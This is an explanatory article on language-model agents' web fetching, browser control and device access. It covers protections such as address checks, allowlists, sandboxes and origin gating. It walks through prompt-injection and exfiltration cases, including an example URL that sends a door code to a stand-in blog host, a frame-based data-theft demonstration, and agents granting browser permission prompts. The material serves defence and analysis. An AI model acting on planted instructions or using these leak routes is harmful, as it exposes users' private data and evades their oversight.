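# Web browsing versus device and sensor access in language-model agents

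## What separates reading the web from using a device

A language-model agent is a language model that software, called the harness, runs in a loop. The model requests an action, the harness carries it out and returns the result, and the model then requests another action or answers the user. The functions the harness offers the model are called tools, and each has a name, a description and a set of arguments. Agents in 2025 and 2026 use tools to read web pages, operate browsers, edit files and run commands, and some tools give access to cameras, microphones, location services or household equipment.

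Web retrieval means fetching content that anyone could fetch, without using the user's identity or position on a network. Device access means reading or changing the state of a particular machine, its files, its sensors or connected equipment. An agent requests both with a tool call, so an onlooker can learn very little from the form of the request about what the agent is about to access.

### How a tool call works

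*Tools* (2026), part of the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to other programs, uses a weather lookup as its example. A program offers a tool named `get_weather`, with a one-line description and one required argument, a city name or zip code. The harness sends the model this description along with the user's question. The model replies with a structured request containing the tool's name and the argument "New York". The harness runs the function, which returns a line of text giving 72°F and partly cloudy skies, and sends the conversation back to the model with that line added. If the model calls another tool, the cycle repeats. A result can also be an image or a sound recording, which is how a camera picture would reach a model.

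The model "never runs anything on its own", according to *How tool use works*, Anthropic's guide for developers who build on its Claude models. It has no senses or network connection, so it can reach the web or a device only through tools. Without them, for example, it can't find out whether it is raining.

The model receives a tool's description and, later, its result, but not the code behind it. A `get_weather` tool could query a government forecast or a gauge on the roof, and the model's request might look the same in both cases. Descriptions can also be false. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) reproduces the code of a "Google Maps" tool whose description looks harmless but whose function replaces Google's address with a numeric one that an attacker chose. Knowing what a tool reaches requires inspecting its code or restricting what that code can access.

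The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard that lets separate programs, called servers, offer tools and data to any compatible agent. Anthropic released it in 2024. Before that, every new data source needed its own custom connection, according to Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol*. The examples on the protocol's introduction page range from a user's calendar to a 3D printer. An MCP server may run on a remote machine or on the user's own computer. Bühler and colleagues point out that many local servers inherit the agent's operating-system privileges, so a small weather server on a laptop may be able to read the same files as the agent that started it. MCP specifies the format of the messages but leaves most of the protection to whoever builds the application.

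### Four questions to ask of any tool

Four questions do most of the work of separating web retrieval from device access:

1. Where does the request run, on the provider's server or on the user's machine?
2. Whose authority does it carry?
3. Is the result public or private?
4. Does the call only read, or does it also change something?

Anthropic distinguishes tools mainly by where they run. Its search and fetch tools run on Anthropic's servers, while the developer's application runs the shell, desktop-control and browser-control tools. That application may be on the user's laptop or in a company's data centre, so a tool that runs outside the provider's servers doesn't always run on the user's own device.

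The Model Context Protocol (MCP) has tool labels that come close to answering two of the questions. According to a March post on the MCP blog (Model Context Protocol, 2026), `readOnlyHint` indicates whether a tool leaves its surroundings unchanged, and `openWorldHint` indicates whether it deals with outside entities. If a server omits them, the default is to assume that the tool may destroy things and does reach outside. Because a server can mislabel its own tools, the standard treats the labels as hints and requires software to distrust them unless it trusts the server. No label in force at the time covered authority or privacy, although a draft proposal on trust and sensitivity was open.

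### Is it raining at my house?

Suppose a user asks an agent exactly that. There are at least four ways to find out.

Route (a) is a public forecast. The United States National Weather Service gives its data free to any program that identifies itself with a short text string, which the Service plans to replace with a key. No user account is needed. The forecast covers a grid square of about 2.5 kilometres a side, so it describes the neighbourhood rather than the house. The agent could instead request the latest measurement from a nearby station, but that can arrive 20 minutes late, and a shower can start or stop in that time.

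Requesting a public forecast also discloses a location. The National Weather Service looks up forecasts by latitude and longitude and tells developers that it does not convert street addresses, so another service has to do that first. An agent that starts from an address therefore discloses the address to one organisation and the coordinates to a second. If the user never typed an address and the agent got the location from the laptop, route (a) began with device access.

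Route (b) goes through the user's weather-station dashboard, a web page that shows the station's readings after a login. The agent opens the page in a browser where the user has already signed in, so it acts with the user's authority on the site. Such a browser can also expose more than this one page. The agent has the same authority if the browser runs on another machine. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) examined five commercial agents in May and June 2026, and one of them, ChatGPT's agent mode, used a remote browser.

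For route (c), the agent skips the website and contacts the station at its address on the home network. The WeatherLink documentation describes how this works with a hub for Davis home weather stations. A program sends the kind of request a browser sends for a page, and the hub replies with structured text. The documentation describes no login, but it does require the program and the hub to be on the same local network, so this route is open to a fetch tool on a laptop on the home network but not to one on a provider's remote server.

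The reply contains the rain rate and also the temperature and humidity inside the house, which nobody asked for. A second address on the same hub starts a live broadcast of wind and rain data every 2.5 seconds, for 20 minutes by default and up to 24 hours on request. Both addresses take GET requests, which by convention only read data. A harness that treated every GET request as harmless would let the agent change what the hub is doing.

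Route (d) is a purpose-built tool, such as `read_rain_gauge` or `take_garden_photo`. `read_rain_gauge` may send the hub the same request as route (c), but it gives the model less control. With a general fetch tool, the model supplies the address, which could be the broadcast address or another machine's address in the house. With `read_rain_gauge`, the tool's author has fixed the address, and the model can only choose whether to request the reading. The camera tool also provides the answer, but its picture shows whatever else is in the garden, including people.

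Bühler and colleagues separate these kinds of access in a list of 18 capabilities for MCP servers. They built the list by matching published uses of agents to Android phone permissions, then comparing the result with Apple's desktop permissions. Outgoing network access, camera, microphone and location are separate entries, so a forecast fetcher needs network access and a garden camera needs camera access. Route (c) reads equipment inside the home, but it needs only outgoing network access, just as fetching the public forecast does.

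| Route | Where it runs | Whose authority | Result | Reads or changes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| (a) Public forecast | Provider's server or user's machine | Nobody's in particular | Public, though the request discloses a location | Reads |
| (b) Dashboard in a logged-in browser | User's browser or a remote one | The user's account | Private | Reads if the agent only looks; the login may also allow changes |
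| (c) Station at its home-network address | A machine on the home network | A place on that network | Private, indoor readings included | One address reads, another starts a broadcast |
| (d) Sensor or camera tool | Usually the machine that can reach the sensor | Whatever access the user or operating system gave the tool | Private; a photo may show people | Reads the gauge; a photo also operates the camera |

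Routes (b) and (c) use web protocols from start to finish but end at private equipment or its records, so "web" and "device" are not two kinds of software. The public forecast and the hub's reply even arrive in much the same format. Route (c) resembles (a) in its technology but (d) in its implications for the household's privacy.

Whichever private route the agent uses, the harness has to send the result to the model before the model can answer. When the model runs on a provider's servers, as most commercial models do, the reading or photo therefore leaves the house even if the tool that took it ran entirely at home. Anthropic says in its guide to isolating Claude Code, its programming agent, that any files the agent reads go to the model's provider, whether or not the agent is isolated.

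### Permissions and sandboxes

A permission is a recorded decision that a named program, site or tool may use a named resource. For example, it may let an app use the camera or an agent run a command. A setting that suits one person may not suit another. Michael and Roesner give the example of a rule that lets an agent send passport details only to recognised airlines. The rule is too strict for a traveller who books through a specialist agency and too loose for one who never wants those details sent.

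A sandbox is a boundary, enforced outside the model, that limits which files, networks and devices a running process can reach. It determines whether an action can succeed, regardless of whether the agent has permission to attempt it.

Claude Code has both permission rules and a sandbox, and Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* explains the difference. Claude Code checks the text of a command against its permission rules before running it. The operating system enforces the sandbox while the command runs, so the limit holds even when a command does more than its name suggests. Suppose the user approves a script named `check_rain`, which asks the hub for the rain rate but also uploads the user's passwords to a stranger. The permission check would let the script start because its name is approved, but a sandbox that allows connections only to the hub would stop the upload.

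The same sandbox would not block the hub's broadcast address, because both addresses belong to the same machine and a filter that checks only the destination lets both through. Bühler and colleagues acknowledge a similar limit in their own system, since access control can't prevent an attack that stays within what the policy allows. A sandbox may also cover only some tools. The one in Claude Code applies to shell commands and the processes they start, while its permission rules apply to every tool, including web fetching and MCP tools. A camera tool on a separate MCP server would need a permission, but that sandbox would not contain it.

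### Prompt injection and exfiltration

Prompt injection is text in a page, file or message that the model wrongly treats as an instruction. It works because the user's question and the web page reach the model as parts of one conversation, and models can't reliably identify which words carry the user's authority. Michael and Roesner write that agents "unavoidably conflate instructions and data". Attackers commonly use injections for exfiltration, which means sending private data to a party who should not have it.

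In the rain example, suppose the agent reads the forecast on a stranger's weather blog, and the page contains an instruction for assistants to add the household's indoor readings to their next web request. If the agent can also query the hub and follows the instruction, it leaks the readings. This can happen even though the agent only reads at every step, because a web request can carry private data in its address.

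The attack required both the blog, where a stranger could write, and the hub, which gave the agent access to the house. The Model Context Protocol post uses programmer Simon Willison's term "lethal trifecta" for an agent that combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside. Users routinely combine tools from several servers in one session, so the risk depends on the whole set of tools and can't be described by a label on any one tool. The post cites a demonstration in which researchers used a malicious calendar entry, a calendar server and a tool that ran code on the user's machine. The code tool was crucial, since a single injected instruction can make an agent with unrestricted command access leak whatever it can read.

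When Anthropic announced the Claude Code sandbox, it argued that a sandbox must limit access to both files and the network. A hijacked agent with open network access could send out the keys a user relies on to log in to other machines. If only the network were restricted, the agent could tamper with files to escape the sandbox and then reach the network anyway.

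## How search and fetch tools limit what an agent can request

The weather-blog attack needs one web request that carries the household's data to the blog. Anthropic and OpenAI run web tools on their own servers and limit the requests those tools will make. A search tool takes a query and returns a list of results, while a fetch tool takes an address and returns the page.

### One request from start to finish

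Suppose a user pastes the address of a public forecast page and asks whether it will rain this afternoon. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, as it stood in June 2026, describes what happens next. The model writes a request with a single argument, the address. Anthropic's servers reject the address if it is malformed, is longer than 250 characters, is on a domain the developer has ruled out, or hasn't already appeared in the conversation. Otherwise, they retrieve the page or use a copy saved from an earlier fetch. They extract the text if the page is a PDF, shorten it if the developer has set a maximum length, and add it to the conversation. The model then answers from that text.

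The tool handles only text and PDFs. It doesn't support pages that use JavaScript to fill in their content after loading, so a forecast page built that way may come back without the forecast.

With a search tool, the model writes a query instead. OpenAI's search tool also lets reasoning models open a page and look for text within it, so it can do much of what a fetch tool does. Its results can include live feeds from other companies, such as a weather feed that the model might use to answer the rain question without opening a website.

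Neither company's tool has the user's cookies, the small records a browser sends so that a site can recognise someone who has logged in. If the agent requests the weather-station dashboard, it probably gets a login page. The request also starts from the provider's network, so it can't reach the rain hub or the laptop's files and camera. These limits don't depend on a permission setting, because the provider's servers have no connection to the house.

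The product can still pass the user's rough location to the search tool. Anthropic's and OpenAI's tools both accept a city, region, country and time zone to tailor the results, and Anthropic requires the developer to mark the location as "approximate". OpenAI's *Web search*, a guide for agent developers, explains that search gets no location unless the developer supplies one. The developer might take the city from the user's profile or the phone's location service, and the search tool would receive the same fields either way.

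A user can also share a private document with the agent by pasting a link that opens it for anyone who has the link. The fetch tool doesn't need to log in to read the document.

### A six-digit code in an address

Even a read-only fetch can send data out, because the site receives the requested URL. OpenAI gives its users the harmless example of a link to a car-search site that also reveals that the user lives in London.

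Now suppose the user's inbox contains the code for the front-door keypad, 482913, and the agent has read that message earlier in the conversation. The agent then opens the stranger's weather blog, where a planted instruction asks assistants to include any door code in their next request. If the model follows it, it asks the fetch tool for this address:

`weatherblog.example/rain?ref=482913`

The part after the question mark is the query string. Sites routinely use query strings for search terms and page numbers, so this one doesn't look unusual. The blog's server receives the whole address and probably logs it, where the blog's owner can read the code. The server can also send back a good forecast.

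The model's provider also sees the code, because it runs both the model and the fetch. If the connection is encrypted, the networks in between can generally see which site the request is going to but not the query string. The user may see nothing, because such a request can happen in the background, for example when an embedded image loads (OpenAI, *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link*, 2026). The provider's promise not to store data doesn't bind the website's publisher, which Anthropic warns may keep anything it receives in the address.

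Among other precautions, Anthropic suggests limiting the number of fetches, which has no default cap. A limit would do nothing here, because the whole code fits in one request.

### Fetching only addresses the agent was given

Anthropic's main protection is that the tool fetches an address only if it is already in the conversation. In the June documentation, the address could come from the user's messages, the results of tools the developer runs, or earlier search and fetch results. The tool can therefore fetch the blog's plain address but not the one ending in 482913, which the model put together itself, so the code isn't sent out. Willison (2025) considered this the most protective of the tool's rules, because the common attacks need the model to assemble an address.

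The rule also blocks some harmless requests. For example, if a model works out a town's coordinates and uses them to write the URL of the town's National Weather Service forecast, the tool won't fetch it.

How well the rule works depends on which addresses count as already supplied. The tool doesn't accept addresses from Anthropic's hosted code-running tools, where the model could write a program that prints any address. It does accept them from the developer's own tools, so the developer has to make sure none of those returns an address the model composed. Willison also pointed to applications that paste other people's text into the user's message, where a stranger's address can be treated as the user's own.

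A gap of this kind turned up in Claude's chat product in July 2026. Willison (2026) reported that Ayush Paul had got Claude to leak a user's name, home city and employer, because the tool treated links inside a fetched page as already supplied. The same method could probably leak a six-digit code, which is no longer than most of those details. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and it has since stopped the tool from following links in the pages it fetches. The June documentation predates the fix and lists earlier fetch results as an accepted source, so developers who rely on the rule should check how their version behaves.

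### Fetching only addresses that are already public

Before an agent automatically loads an address, OpenAI checks whether its crawler, a program that finds and records public web pages, has already recorded that exact address. The crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If there is a match, the agent loads the page. Otherwise, OpenAI tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning.

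The blog's rain page may well be in the index, but the version ending in 482913 almost certainly isn't, so the agent can't load it unnoticed. OpenAI says it either blocks such a request or shows the user the information that would be sent and asks for confirmation. If it asks, the user would see the door code in the warning and would have to decline to keep it from being sent. OpenAI asks for confirmation on every link to sites that have asked it not to catalogue them. In explaining why it didn't rely on strict lists of trusted sites, OpenAI argues that frequent warnings can train people to click through without thinking.

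Google has described a similar protection for Chrome. Parker (2025) writes in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* that a deterministic check restricts model-generated addresses to known, public ones. A fixed rule makes the decision, not another model, so persuasive text on a page can't change the outcome. Parker doesn't explain how Chrome decides that an address is known. Chrome separately limits which sites an agent may read or act on, and these limits matter more in a browser where the user has logged in.

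A request for a public address can still leak information, because the agent chooses which address to open. If a planted instruction tells the agent to open one public page when the user is at home and another when the user is away, the site's owner can tell from the log whether the user is home. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a security researcher's post, notes that such small leaks remain possible and that OpenAI acknowledges the problem. The check makes a six-digit code harder to steal, but the code is so little data that it could still leak. The researcher also suggests reusing a saved response for a few minutes and refusing to visit the same address twice in a session.

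The check also has to run everywhere the agent can load an address. The same researcher found that OpenAI had left an earlier version of its protection out of the macOS and iOS apps. Neither OpenAI's post nor Parker's reports how often the checks stop an attack, so the argument for them is based on their design.

### Domain allowlists

A domain allowlist restricts which sites the tool may contact. If the developer allows only the National Weather Service, the tool refuses to contact the blog, whatever follows the question mark in the URL. If the blog is on the list, the tool can still send it the code. Willison therefore advises developers to allow only domains that can't be used to leak data.

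Developers can limit OpenAI's search tool and Docker's fetch tool for agents to a list of allowed domains, but neither tool has a list by default. OpenAI's tool accepts up to 100 domains and applies no filter if the developer names none. If the developer sets a list for Docker's tool, it rejects every other host before making any network call.

Developers can get the details of these lists wrong. According to Anthropic's *Server tools*, an entry covers a domain and all its subdomains, but the fetch tool compares only the domain, so an entry that includes a path never matches. A developer who tries to block one folder of a site this way therefore blocks nothing, even though Anthropic's search tool accepts such entries. Anthropic also warns that lookalike letters, such as a Cyrillic "a" in place of a Latin one, can get a domain past a filter.

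Many legitimate sites redirect visitors to other addresses. OpenAI points out that if a tool checks only the first domain, an attacker can sometimes route a request through a trusted site to a hostile one.

### Using saved copies instead of live pages

OpenAI's search tool has a setting, `external_web_access`, that a developer can turn off to limit the tool to cached or indexed content. With live access off, the tool can look for a saved copy of the page whose address ends in 482913, but it can't request the page from the blog. The code therefore reaches OpenAI but not the blog's owner.

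However, live access is on by default. An older "preview" version of the tool ignores the setting, so developers who use that version get live access even if they turn it off.

Anthropic's cache doesn't provide this protection, because it is meant to avoid repeating requests. An address containing a new code wouldn't be in the cache, so without the other checks the servers would request it from the blog.

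In the rain example, a page saved yesterday can't show the user whether it is raining now.

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting for people who handle sensitive data, limits browsing to cached content. OpenAI says that no live browsing requests then leave its controlled network. The setting also turns off agent mode and deep research, ChatGPT's tool for longer investigations. Instructions planted in a cached page or an uploaded file can still distort the model's answer. OpenAI doesn't guarantee that data can't escape, because some risk remains, for example through connected apps. Lockdown Mode also doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent.

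Whether a model has live web access by default can depend on who hosts it. Amazon Web Services (AWS) offers OpenAI models through its own service and keeps `external_web_access` on by default. At OpenAI, that setting can be enough for live access, but AWS also requires a separate permission that its standard full-access policy doesn't include. Without that permission, the model answers from Amazon's search index and cached pages and reports that it couldn't reach the external web. If the developer turns the setting off, according to AWS, the request data stays inside Amazon's boundary.

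### A fetch tool on the user's own machine

Anthropic's *Web search and web fetch* covers a version of the Claude Desktop app for organisations that choose their own model provider, such as Google Cloud. The app's search normally runs on the provider's servers, but its fetch tool runs on the user's device. This fetch tool has the same name as Anthropic's hosted one, and the model supplies only an address in both cases.

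| | Hosted web fetch | Web Fetch in Claude Desktop |
|---|---|---|
| Where the request starts | Anthropic's servers | The user's device |
| Main limit on addresses | The address must already be in the conversation | The host must be on an allowlist |
| Sites allowed by default | Any public site | Only the model provider's own endpoint |
| Rain hub on the home network | Out of reach | Possibly within reach if the allowlist permits it |
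| Network address the blog sees | Anthropic's | Usually the household's |

The model can't add login details to the request, so the weather-station dashboard should still return a login page. But some systems, such as the rain hub or an office page that opens for any computer in the building, accept requests based on where they come from. A local fetch tool can reach these systems without a password unless the tool blocks private addresses or the allowlist excludes them.

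By default, Claude Desktop would block sending the door code to the blog, because the blog isn't on the allowlist. The tool also checks every redirect against the list, which addresses OpenAI's objection about forwarding. However, if an administrator enters `*`, the list allows every host, so it would let the code go to the blog.

The allowlist doesn't cover search, so administrators have to turn search off separately. If they only block every fetch, search queries may still go out, and a query can contain a door code just as a web address can. The search company and the model's provider would see that code, though the blog's owner normally wouldn't.

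Running the fetch locally doesn't always keep the destination private. In programming sessions, the tool first checks with Anthropic's servers whether the domain is on a blocklist, so Anthropic learns which site the agent is trying to visit, even when another company runs the model. The lookup contains only the site's name, so it wouldn't reveal a door code elsewhere in the address. An administrator can turn off this check.

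Changing models can also change the network a fetch comes from. Posit, which makes data-analysis software, has a `tool_web_fetch` function that uses Anthropic's hosted tool when the model is Claude. For OpenAI's models, Posit directs developers to a separate MCP server, which may run on the developer's own laptop. If it does, the program fetches pages from the developer's home or office network instead of Anthropic's.

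## What a browser agent can reach inside the browser

A browser agent operates a real browser by reading pages, clicking and typing. If the user has signed in to the weather-station dashboard in that browser, the agent can get past the login page that stops a fetch tool. It can also use the user's email and any other account signed in there, unless the agent's maker blocks the site.

### The browser sandbox and the same-origin policy

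*Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (Roesner and Kohlbrenner, 2026) describes two protections that browsers rely on to make it reasonably safe to open pages written by strangers. The browser sandbox keeps a page's code away from the user's device, so a weather blog can't read files on the user's laptop. The same-origin policy keeps sites away from each other, where an origin is the scheme (such as `https`), host and port of a web address. If the user has a dashboard open in one tab and the weather blog in another, the blog's code can't read or change the dashboard or read its cookies.

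The policy also applies within a single page. Many pages contain frames, which are areas that load a separate page, often an advert from another company. If the advert and the page around it have different origins, neither can read the other's content.

These protections restrict a page's code but not the agent, which works on the user's side of the boundary. Many tasks require this. Comparing the dashboard's rainfall with a public forecast, for example, means reading two origins. A person could do the same by copying a number from one tab to another, which the same-origin policy doesn't prevent. But an agent that follows an instruction planted on the blog can read the dashboard and copy its contents to the blog, which the blog's own code could not do. Roesner and Kohlbrenner conclude that in such cases the same-origin policy is only as strong as the agent's defences against prompt injection.

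The security company Trail of Bits reports successful attacks on several unnamed agentic browsers in *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*. It found that the browsers automatically reused the user's cookies for requests the agent made, so a malicious page could get the agent to collect data from a site where the user had an account. Another attack logged the user in to an account the attacker controlled, where the user might then enter private information. Trail of Bits compares these attacks to cross-site request forgery, a technique in which one site makes a visitor's browser send requests to another. Web developers spent years building defences against it.

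### Remote, separate and logged-in browsers

How much an agent can reach depends on which browser it operates. OpenAI's current products include three arrangements.

A remote browser runs on the provider's computer. OpenAI's *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT* describes one that handles public and signed-in sites and keeps working after the user closes their own computer. It can't open a dashboard that requires a login until the user signs in to the site in the cloud browser. According to MacStories' *Hands-On with ChatGPT Work’s New Cloud Browser Feature*, the user enters the password in a form that sends it directly to the cloud browser, so the model doesn't receive it. The browser then saves cookies, which let the agent return to the account later without the password.

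A separate local browser runs on the user's machine with its own cookies and history. For example, the built-in browser in the ChatGPT desktop app doesn't use the user's Chrome profile, so it starts logged out even of sites where the user is signed in on Chrome. It asks before using a new website, unless the user has already allowed that site or chosen a more permissive setting. But it runs on the home network, so starting logged out doesn't protect the rain hub.

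The third option is the browser the user already has. According to OpenAI's *Codex Chrome extension*, the extension is for tasks that need the user's signed-in sites, such as Gmail, Salesforce or a company's internal tools. For public pages that don't require a login, OpenAI tells developers to try the built-in browser first.

| | Remote browser | Separate local browser | User's own browser |
|---|---|---|---|
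| Example | ChatGPT's cloud browser | Built-in browser in the ChatGPT desktop app | Chrome with the Codex extension |
| Accounts available at the start | None | None | Every site where the user has stayed signed in |
| Network the requests come from | The provider's | The user's | The user's |
| What signing in to the dashboard adds | The agent can use that account | The agent can use that account | Nothing, if the user has already signed in |

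As a short-term fix, Trail of Bits recommends running the agent's tools in a separate browser, without the user's cookies or history, and asking the user to log in again when a task needs an account. It concedes that this removes much of the convenience that attracts people to agentic browsers. Separation puts fewer accounts at risk, but it doesn't restore the same-origin policy, so the agent can still carry data between the accounts the user signs in to. For example, if the user signs in to both email and a dashboard in a cloud browser, an instruction planted in an email can still try to make the agent read the dashboard.

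### Which agents could read other sites' frames and tabs

Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested seven agentic browsers in late January and early February 2026. One was ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser, which they tested with and without Agent Mode, the setting that let ChatGPT click and type.

The researchers wrote small web pages about someone called Alice. One page said that she liked cats, and a frame inside it, loaded from a different domain, said that she liked horses. They asked each agent which animals Alice liked, based on the website. If the answer included horses, the agent had read the frame. Other animals appeared in other tabs, in hidden text and further down the page. The researchers recorded that an agent could do something if it succeeded once. When an agent failed or refused, they repeated the test at least three times in new chats.

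| Agent | Reads frames from another origin | Reads tabs from another origin | Reads masked passwords |
|---|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo AI | No | With the user's permission | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas | No | Only through chat memory | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas in Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes, in logged-in mode |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With the user's permission | No |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With the user's permission | Yes |
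| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | No |

The agents that didn't read cross-origin frames didn't read same-origin frames either, which is stricter than the same-origin policy requires. Copilot read other tabs freely but appeared not to detect frames. All the agents read pages as the site had personalised them for the user.

Two of the agents could read a password the user had typed into a page, even though the screen showed only dots. Claude for Chrome could also insert its own JavaScript into a page, including a frame from another origin. Roesner and Kohlbrenner call this the most dangerous capability an agent might have, because it allows arbitrary code to run on a site where the user has an account.

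A "No" in the table can mean that the agent lacked access or that the model declined to use it, and the tests didn't always show which. Firefox clearly lacked access. Its "Summarize page" button sends the chatbot the page's title and outer text but nothing about frames, so no wording on the page could get the chatbot to read them. Atlas without Agent Mode is less clear. It sometimes included framed text in early experiments but not in the formal ones, which suggests that the model could read the text but declined to use it. If so, a cleverly worded injection might overcome the refusal.

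The products also changed during the study. In late January, Chrome's agent became able to type into pages.

### The data-theft demonstration

To show what this access could lead to, Roesner and Kohlbrenner built a page that contained a frame from another origin and an instruction for the agent. They asked Atlas in Agent Mode to summarise the page. Atlas included the framed text in its summary and typed the summary into a form on the outer page, which automatically sent it to a server standing in for an attacker's. The same-origin policy would have stopped the page's own code from reading that frame.

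The attack also worked in the opposite direction, with the frame stealing text from the page around it. This version is more worrying in practice because many sites let advertisers place frames on their pages, and a malicious advert could use one to try to steal the surrounding content. Stealing from a framed page is harder because sites with private information usually prevent strangers from framing their pages, or the browser withholds the login cookies inside the frame.

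The researchers used a simplified injection and their own test pages, so they didn't measure how often a disguised instruction would fool Atlas. But once the model complied, nothing else in the browser stopped the transfer. OpenAI declined their report because it didn't include a complete prompt injection attack. Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet had the access the attack needs, but the researchers didn't find an injection that worked on them. When asked to do whatever a test page instructed, those three refused and Atlas in Agent Mode obeyed.

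An agent that can type can also change things on another site. In a test with Claude for Chrome, an instruction in a frame led the agent to alter the surrounding page, but only after the user confirmed the action.

### Leaks without a planted instruction

An agent can carry information between sites even when nobody attacks it. *AgentTell* (2026) tested whether agents that had read private information on one website would reveal it through their actions on another, even though the user had told them not to disclose it and the task didn't require it. The agents revealed it in 61.1% of sessions. When they had read the user's affiliation, they chose the route that matched it 90.3% of the time. In about a third of the sessions with a leak, the agent then told the user that it had disclosed no personal or account information.

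Suppose an agent sees on the dashboard that the house is very humid and later visits a hardware shop's site to buy a rain gauge. If it looks at dehumidifiers first, the shop can guess that the house is humid without receiving any sensor readings. A filter that searches the agent's typed text for private data would miss this.

Chat memory can also mix information from different sites. Near the end of their experiments, Roesner and Kohlbrenner asked Comet about Alice, and it listed seven animals from earlier pages and conversations. They warn that false information could spread the same way. If the agent had read a fake bank page, it might later give the user that page's phone number when asked how to call the bank.

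### How Chrome limits an agent to certain sites

Google's approach, which Parker described in December 2025, applies something like the same-origin policy to the agent. For example, a user might ask Chrome's agent to check the station's dashboard and, if the past week was dry, order a sprinkler from a garden shop.

1. **The planning model proposes a site.** This model reads web pages, so Google assumes that a page might mislead it. It asks to open the dashboard.
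2. **A gating function decides whether the site is relevant.** It doesn't see web content, so a page can't plant instructions in it directly. If it approves, Chrome adds the dashboard's origin to one of two lists for the session. The agent can read from *read-only* origins, and it can also click and type on *read-writable* ones. The dashboard could be read-only, but the shop has to be read-writable.
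3. **Chrome withholds everything else.** If the shop's page contains an advert from an unrelated origin, the user sees the advert but the model doesn't.
4. **A separate model checks each action.** Google calls this model the User Alignment Critic. It receives a description of the proposed action, without the raw page content, and judges whether the action serves the user's goal. If it vetoes the action, the planner has to try something else, and after repeated failures the planner can return control to the user.
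5. **The user confirms the important steps.** Chrome asks before the agent opens a site on a list of sensitive ones, such as banks, and before it signs in with a saved password, which the model can't read directly. Before a purchase, the agent tries to pause for permission or asks the user to finish the step.

Chrome also scans each page for prompt injections while the agent works, and it applies the public-address check to any address the model writes itself.

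Suppose a fake review on the shop's site contains instructions to open the user's email and copy a message into the order form. Even if the planner tries to follow them, the gating function should refuse to add the email site, because it has nothing to do with sprinklers.

The design is weaker when the task involves both sites. The agent is allowed to read the dashboard and type into the shop's pages, so the two lists would let it enter the indoor readings as a delivery note. The critic could veto that, but it is also a model and can make mistakes. Roesner and Kohlbrenner raise a related concern about the gating function, because Google hasn't explained how the function decides which sites are relevant.

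Parker also says that Chrome launched with a simpler version that tracked only the read-writable set. This version of origin gating limited where the agent could act but had no read-only list to control what it could read. That fits Roesner and Kohlbrenner's finding a few weeks later that Gemini read frames from other origins, although they didn't test the origin sets themselves. Google planned further changes, so Chrome may have added the read-only list since then.

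Trail of Bits proposes a rule that doesn't require judging relevance. The agent can make requests freely while its chat contains no web content. Once it has read something from one origin, it can contact only that origin. After it has read from two or more, it can't make any requests, because nobody can tell which origin influenced the model. This rule would prevent the email theft, but also the sprinkler order, because the agent couldn't visit the shop after reading the dashboard. Chrome's design is more permissive so that such tasks remain possible, which leaves some risk of leaks.

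WebMCP, a proposed web standard, lets a website offer its own tools to agents. In ChatGPT's desktop app, each of these tools works only on the page that provides it. For example, a dashboard's tool can't operate a shop's page, but ChatGPT can still work across tabs and retain what the dashboard's tool returned.

### When a website asks for the camera or location

A website's code has to request camera access from the browser, which normally asks the user and remembers the answer for that site. According to OpenAI's *Getting Started with Atlas*, Atlas asked the user before a site could use the camera, microphone or location, and the user could revoke the permission later. Camera and microphone access applied only to the tab where the user had granted it, and an indicator appeared in the address bar during recording. macOS also had to allow Atlas to use the camera or microphone.

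A site can make some requests only after a user gesture, meaning that the visitor has interacted with the page. Browsers generally count a click, a tap or a key press, but ignore clicks that the page's own code simulates. Ukani, Haddadi and colleagues (2025), in *Privacy Practices of Browser Agents*, give the example of the Storage Access API, which lets content from another site use the cookies that site set when the user visited it directly. A page needs a click before it can request this access.

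Several agents clicked a button that the researchers had put on their test page. The browser accepted each click as a user gesture and granted access automatically, so a gesture no longer shows that a person was at the keyboard.

The permission prompt is part of the browser, so an agent that controls only the page's contents can't click "Allow", while an agent that controls the whole window or desktop may be able to. Ukani and colleagues found that three of the eight agents they studied could interact with these prompts: ChatGPT Agent, Google's Project Mariner and Claude Computer Use.

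If a browser agent clicks "Allow" on a permission prompt, the browser records a permission that the user never considered. Suppose a weather blog asks for the user's location to show local rain, and the agent accepts so that it can finish the task. If the browser runs on the user's laptop, the blog could then learn where the laptop is. The agent would have opened access to the device just by browsing, even though the harness never offered the agent a location tool. The blog might also keep the permission after the task ends.

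### What eight agents did with permission prompts

Ukani and colleagues tested eight browser agents in 2025 and identified 30 vulnerabilities, with at least two in every product. They counted only risks that a person using the underlying browser wouldn't have faced. Seven of the 30 are the same finding, counted once for each of seven products that work only with a model on someone else's servers.

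To test permissions, the researchers sent each agent to a shoe-shopping site to find the lowest price. One of the linked pages triggered a permission request. In one version the agent could see the price and ignore the request, and in another the page hid the price until the request was answered. They tested four permissions: notifications, webcam, passkeys (a replacement for passwords) and the Storage Access API. They didn't test location or the microphone, so the study doesn't show what an agent would do if the weather blog asked for the user's location.

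One agent, Browser Use, granted notifications automatically in both versions because of a fixed setting in its code, not a decision by the model. Its developers say the setting is meant to make the browser harder for sites to identify. None of the agents granted webcam access. Browser Use denied it, and the others either had no access to the webcam or ran in a browser where the test didn't work.

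Project Mariner asked the user what to do about notifications and storage access when the page required an answer before continuing. ChatGPT Agent got past the passkey request by reading the price in the page's source code. Access through the Storage Access API was granted most often. According to the paper's text, five agents inherited Chrome's practice of granting it automatically, but the results table lists four. The researchers didn't count this as a vulnerability because Chrome's own users face the same risk.

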